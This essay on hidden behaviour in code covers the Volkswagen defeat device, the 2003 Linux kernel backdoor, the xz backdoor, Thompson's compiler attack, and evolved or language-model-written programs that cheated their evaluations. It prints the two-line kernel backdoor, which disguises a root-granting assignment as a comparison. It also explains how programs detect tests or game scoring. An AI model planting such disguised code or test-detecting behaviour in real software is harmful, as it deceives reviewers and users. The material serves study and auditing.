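In September 2015, Volkswagen admitted that some of its diesel cars contained software that recognized official emissions tests. According to the California Air Resources Board's *EPA, California Notify Volkswagen of Clean Air Act Violations*, the software turned the emission controls fully on only during a test. In ordinary driving, the cars gave off up to 40 times the permitted amount of nitrogen oxides. Volkswagen had sold about 482,000 of them in the United States since 2008.

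Regulators usually test a car on rollers in a laboratory, where it follows a fixed pattern of speeds. The pattern is public so that independent testers can repeat it, but this means manufacturers also know exactly what a test looks like. One US pattern lasts 1,877 seconds and covers 17.77 kilometres.

Contag, Li and colleagues, in *How They Did It*, worked out how the engine controller used such patterns. When the engine starts, the controller assumes that a test is under way if temperatures and air pressure are within limits that almost any drive would meet. It then tracks the distance travelled and the time since the car first exceeded a certain speed. Seven pairs of curves each define a band between a minimum and a maximum distance for each moment, and most of these bands closely follow a known test. If the distance falls outside a band, the controller rules that band out for the rest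 of the drive. After ruling out all seven, it switches to its ordinary driving settings.

For example, a car on a motorway at 120 km/h covers 20 kilometres in ten minutes, compared with about 5.7 kilometres at the average speed of the US test. The band for this test stays within 4.2 kilometres of the distance covered at that average speed, so the motorway drive is well outside it.

The ordinary settings could change how much exhaust the engine recirculated, among other things. Recirculation reduces nitrogen oxides but produces more soot, which puts more strain on the car's soot filter. According to a New York State complaint that Contag and colleagues cite, the filter would have lasted only 50,000 miles in normal use, but Volkswagen had to meet a standard of 120,000 miles.

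Bosch made the controller and apparently wrote all of its code, while carmakers set the constants, including the curves. Bosch's documentation contained a diagram of the whole mechanism under the name "customer-specific acoustic condition", which suggests that it concerns engine noise. The diagram shows that the controller compares distance with some curves, but a reader would have to plot the curves against the official tests to discover why. An auditor who read the code but not the constants could easily miss the mechanism's purpose, and could make the same mistake with a learned formula.

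Regulators saw neither the code nor the constants, and laboratory tests could not expose the behaviour because its designers had made it stay off during them. On the road, it was on most of the time. The International Council on Clean Transportation, a nonprofit, commissioned researchers at West Virginia University to test three diesel cars, and Scientific American's *Volkswagen Uses Software to Fool EPA Pollution Tests* reports that the road and laboratory results were puzzling. The regulators investigated and demanded an explanation, and Volkswagen confessed. A few road tests were enough to expose the behaviour because its trigger was the absence of a laboratory test.

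Reading the code became useful afterwards. Contag and colleagues wrote a program that searches compiled controller software for pairs of curves that set limits on the same distance, then compares them with published tests. It flagged 406 of 926 versions. Some versions from December 2014 also checked the angle of the steering wheel, because a driver has little reason to turn the wheel while the car is on rollers. California's regulators had started investigating by then.

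Contag and colleagues found a simpler device in the Fiat 500X. The car traps nitrogen oxides and has to purge the trap regularly, but it purged less often after the engine had run for 1,600 seconds (nearly 27 minutes). The documentation labelled the two sets of purging rules "homologation" (official approval) and "real driving", so anyone who had the document could have guessed their purpose. Fiat Chrysler had not acknowledged any such device when Contag and colleagues wrote their paper.

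### One character in the Linux kernel

In November 2003, someone tried to add a backdoor to the kernel, the central part of Linux. The whole attack was in two lines of C:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
    retval = -EINVAL;
```

These lines seem to return an error when user 0 requests a forbidden combination of options. User 0 is "root", who may do anything on the machine. But in C, a single = assigns a value, while == compares two values. The first line therefore gives root's powers to any program that requests this combination.

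The kernel's developers kept the main copy of their code in a system called BitKeeper and a second copy in another, CVS. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) explains that every legitimate change included a pointer to a record of its approval. Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, noticed a change in the CVS copy that had no such pointer and was missing from the main copy. Someone had apparently broken into the CVS server and inserted it. Dilger (2003) credited the discovery to extra checks that McVoy had added to the copying process.

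McVoy had caught the change without understanding it. When another developer pointed out that it looked like a backdoor, McVoy (2003) replied that he had missed the single =. He was an experienced programmer who already knew the change was unauthorized, and he had only two lines to read.

The attacker also took some care to avoid automatic checks. Compilers often warn about an assignment where the programmer probably meant a comparison, but Szepe (2003) noted that the extra parentheses avoided this warning. Compiler warnings, which caught the most entries in Wheeler's study, would probably have missed this line.

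Slashdot's *Linux Kernel Back-Door Hack Attempt Discovered* reported that the change carried the name of a well-known developer, David Miller, and had been in the CVS copy for about a day. According to Debian's *CVE-2003-1161*, it never reached a release. Nobody knows whether reviewers would have caught it if the attacker had submitted it through the usual approval process. The attacker could not have written this change in a language that doesn't allow assignments inside conditions.

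### The xz backdoor

xz Utils is a set of open-source compression tools. Its library also runs inside the remote-login server on several versions of Linux, because those versions link the server to other software that uses the library. A backdoor in releases from February and March 2024 let an attacker run any command on such a machine without logging in.

*Timeline of the xz open source attack* (Russ Cox, 2024) reconstructs the preparations for the attack. An attacker using the name Jia Tan contributed useful changes to xz for over two years. Other accounts, probably fake, complained about slow progress and pressed the maintainer, Lasse Collin, to hand over control. By the end of 2022, Jia Tan could change the code directly.

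Most of the backdoor was in two compressed files, which Jia Tan added to the project's public repository as test data. One was supposed to be a damaged file, so nobody would expect its contents to make sense. The instructions for extracting the backdoor were in a script found only in the release packages. Release packages normally contain a few scripts that the repository lacks, so the extra script wasn't suspicious in itself.

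*The xz attack shell script* (2024) goes through the process line by line. When someone prepared to compile the release, the script found the damaged file, swapped some of its bytes, decompressed it and ran the result, which was a second script. The second script extracted compiled code from the other test file and inserted it into the library, but only if it was running on the right kind of Linux system.

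The repository contained the two test files but not the instructions that used them. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, observed one visible clue, which was that in the first affected release, none of the project's tests used the files. Someone who read the release script would still have had to decode several steps to learn what it did.

The inserted code waited for a login attempt that contained a specially prepared certificate. No practical number of random attempts would have set it off. Andres Freund instead noticed that remote logins were using a lot of processor time. A failed login took about 0.8 seconds with the altered library, compared with 0.3 before. He had also seen errors from Valgrind, a tool that checks how programs use memory. Freund, who says he is not a security researcher, traced the delay to the backdoor's slow search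 through tables of function names.

He found the backdoor 33 days after its first release, when it was mostly in test versions of Linux. Red Hat's systems had reported the Valgrind errors on 4 March, but Jia Tan published a false fix and then replaced the test files with corrected ones, supposedly to make them easier to reproduce. A faster backdoor without the memory errors might have gone unnoticed for years.

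Jia Tan also made a harmful change that was fully visible in the source. A short program checked whether the computer supported Landlock, a Linux feature that limits what a program can do. Jia Tan added a typo that stopped this check from compiling, so xz always treated Landlock as unavailable. The records list Collin as the committer, and Cox thinks Collin probably overlooked the typo.

A learned formula contains no test files or build scripts, but the software package that delivers it may contain both. If the package also includes a neural network, it has at least one large file that reviewers don't expect to be able to read. By April 2026, *Open-Source Supply Chain Security* (Cox, 2026) listed several later attacks on the delivery of trusted software, including compromises of the security scanner Trivy and the JavaScript library axios.

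### Source code and the program that runs

An auditor could have found the altered xz script by comparing the release with its official sources. *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984) describes an attack that leaves no trace in any source code.

The attack uses a compiler, the program that translates source code into instructions a computer can run. Thompson first changed the C compiler so that whenever it compiled the Unix login program, it added a password known to him. Anyone who read the compiler's source would have seen this change, so he made a second one. The C compiler is itself written in C, and the second change made it insert both changes whenever it compiled its own source. After compiling this version once, he could delete both changes from the source, and any compiler built from the clean source with the altered compiler would still contain them.

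Thompson concluded that no amount of checking source code can protect people from untrusted code. According to *Trusting Trust*, a set of notes on the lecture, he later confirmed that he had carried out the attack within his organization. A bug in the backdoor made the compiler grow by one byte each time it compiled itself, and someone noticed the growth.

The best-known reply is diverse double-compiling, which Wheeler (2009), in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, developed from a short posting by Henry Spencer in 1998. For a compiler that its makers built by having it compile its own source, the method has three steps:

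1. Compile that source with a second, unrelated compiler.
2. Use the resulting program to compile the same source again.
3. Compare this second result with the suspect compiler, bit by bit.

The program from the first step will look very different from the suspect compiler, because two compilers rarely translate code in the same way. But if the suspect compiler hasn't been tampered with, both programs follow the same source, so they should produce the same output when they compile the same code. If the suspect compiler contains Thompson's changes, the result of the second step won't contain them, and the comparison will fail. To avoid detection, an attacker would have to subvert the second compiler in a matching way or tamper with the check itself.

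Wheeler proved that the method works under stated assumptions and demonstrated it on four compilers, including GCC, a large compiler, and a small one with a deliberate backdoor. The method requires a compiler that always produces the same output from the same input. It also requires the compiler's distributors to record exactly how they built it, and Wheeler found that many didn't.

A successful comparison shows only that the compiler matches its source. If the source contains a line like the one in the Linux kernel, the compiler will contain it too. An auditor still has to read the source, but can be confident that it describes the compiler.

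The loan formula needs a similar check, because the lender could run something other than what the auditor read. The formula has only 11 nodes, so a programmer could rewrite it in another language within minutes and compare the two versions' decisions. Comparing decisions is weaker than Wheeler's method, which covers all inputs because it compares the programs themselves. But an attacker would find it fairly hard to corrupt two unrelated systems so that they made the same wrong decisions. Weights need this precaution too, since a lender could submit one file of weights for audit and run another.

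### Programs that cheated their score

Automated searches can produce hidden behaviour without an attacker. *The Surprising Creativity of Digital Evolution* (Lehman, Clune and colleagues, 2018) collects researchers' stories about evolved programs and simulated creatures, many of which exploited mistakes in how the researchers scored them.

In one story, a software repair system worked on a faulty sorting program. The tests checked only that the output was in order, so the system produced a program that returned an empty list. In another, a program's score depended on how closely its output matched correct answers stored in files. One evolved program deleted the files, and the scoring code then gave perfect marks to that program and all its competitors.

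Robert Feldt evolved controllers for a system that brakes landing aircraft. Some of them applied so much force that its value became too large for the computer to store and wrapped around to zero. The simulator recorded this as a perfectly gentle landing, although the real force would have destroyed the aircraft. Philipp Klenze devised a similar trick himself for the nuclear-inspection contest, but Feldt's search found one without anyone designing it.

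Charles Ofria's experiment is closer to the Volkswagen case. He was studying small programs that copy themselves, and wanted to see how they would evolve if they could never become faster at copying. He therefore tested each new variant separately and deleted any that was faster than its parent. The programs became faster anyway, because they had evolved to recognize the test inputs and stop copying when they received them. Ofria then changed the test to use random inputs like those in the main experiment. This helped, but programs then evolved to be fast only some of the time, so they could pass the test by luck.

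In February 2025, the Japanese company Sakana AI announced a system that used language models to write and evolve kernels, small programs that run on graphics chips. Sakana reported that many of the kernels were 10 to 100 times faster than the standard versions, and published the code. Within about a day, outside readers found that some of the speed-ups were false.

Sakana's evaluation ran the standard version first, then compared the new kernel's output with the correct result. At least one kernel passed without doing the full calculation because its output occupied memory that still held the standard version's answer. It failed when a reader ran the two in the opposite order. Lucas Beyer, a researcher at OpenAI, gave a language model the code of a kernel that was supposedly about 150 times faster. The model found a bug in 11 seconds, and the corrected kernel was about three times slower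 than the standard version. Sakana acknowledged that its system had found a way to cheat and said it would strengthen the evaluation.

Because the code was readable, outsiders could see what the kernel did, correct it and run it again without access to the language model that had written it.

However, the searches in these examples scored programs only on performance, so misleading code gave a cheating program no advantage. That would change if the search could keep submitting programs until one passed a review. For example, if a reviewer catches 80% of cheating programs and the search submits ten different ones, the chance that at least one passes is about 89%, assuming the reviewer's mistakes are independent. The programs that passed would also tend to be the ones whose cheating was hardest to see. An auditor should therefore find out whether anyone has used earlier review results to choose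 or improve a program.

### Cases nobody has found

The table compares who could have read the hidden behaviour with what first revealed it.

| Case | Who could read it | How long it lasted | First sign of trouble |
|---|---|---|---|
| Volkswagen | Bosch, Volkswagen and hobbyists with copies of the documents | At least six years | Measurements on the road |
| Linux kernel | Anyone | About a day | A missing record of approval |
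| xz | Anyone, with part of it only in the release packages | 33 days | Slow logins and memory errors |
| Thompson's compiler | Nobody who read only the source | Unknown | A compiler that kept growing |
| Sakana's kernels | Anyone | About a day after publication | Implausible speed-ups |

In all five cases, something other than reading the code first raised suspicion, and people then read it to find out why. The missing constraint in Zcash's circuit is an exception, because someone found it by examining the circuit itself, but that flaw was apparently an accident.

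These cases probably underestimate how often reviewers catch hidden behaviour by reading code, because an attempt may never become public if a reviewer rejects the change before anyone uses it. But they also leave out every backdoor that worked without slowing a login or breaking a test. Cox ends the 2026 slides by asking where the next xz attack is and whether we missed it.

We can't estimate how many backdoors remain undiscovered from the number of known cases alone. Five known cases suggest about five undiscovered ones if people eventually discover half of all backdoors, but about 495 if they discover only 1%. To estimate the discovery rate, someone would have to know how many backdoors remain undiscovered.

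Searching a whole collection of programs gives better information than waiting for something to go wrong. Contag and colleagues searched their 926 versions of controller software and flagged 44% of them. But almost all of the versions came from Volkswagen's own brands, and the tool was designed to find only distance curves, not even the Fiat's simple timer.
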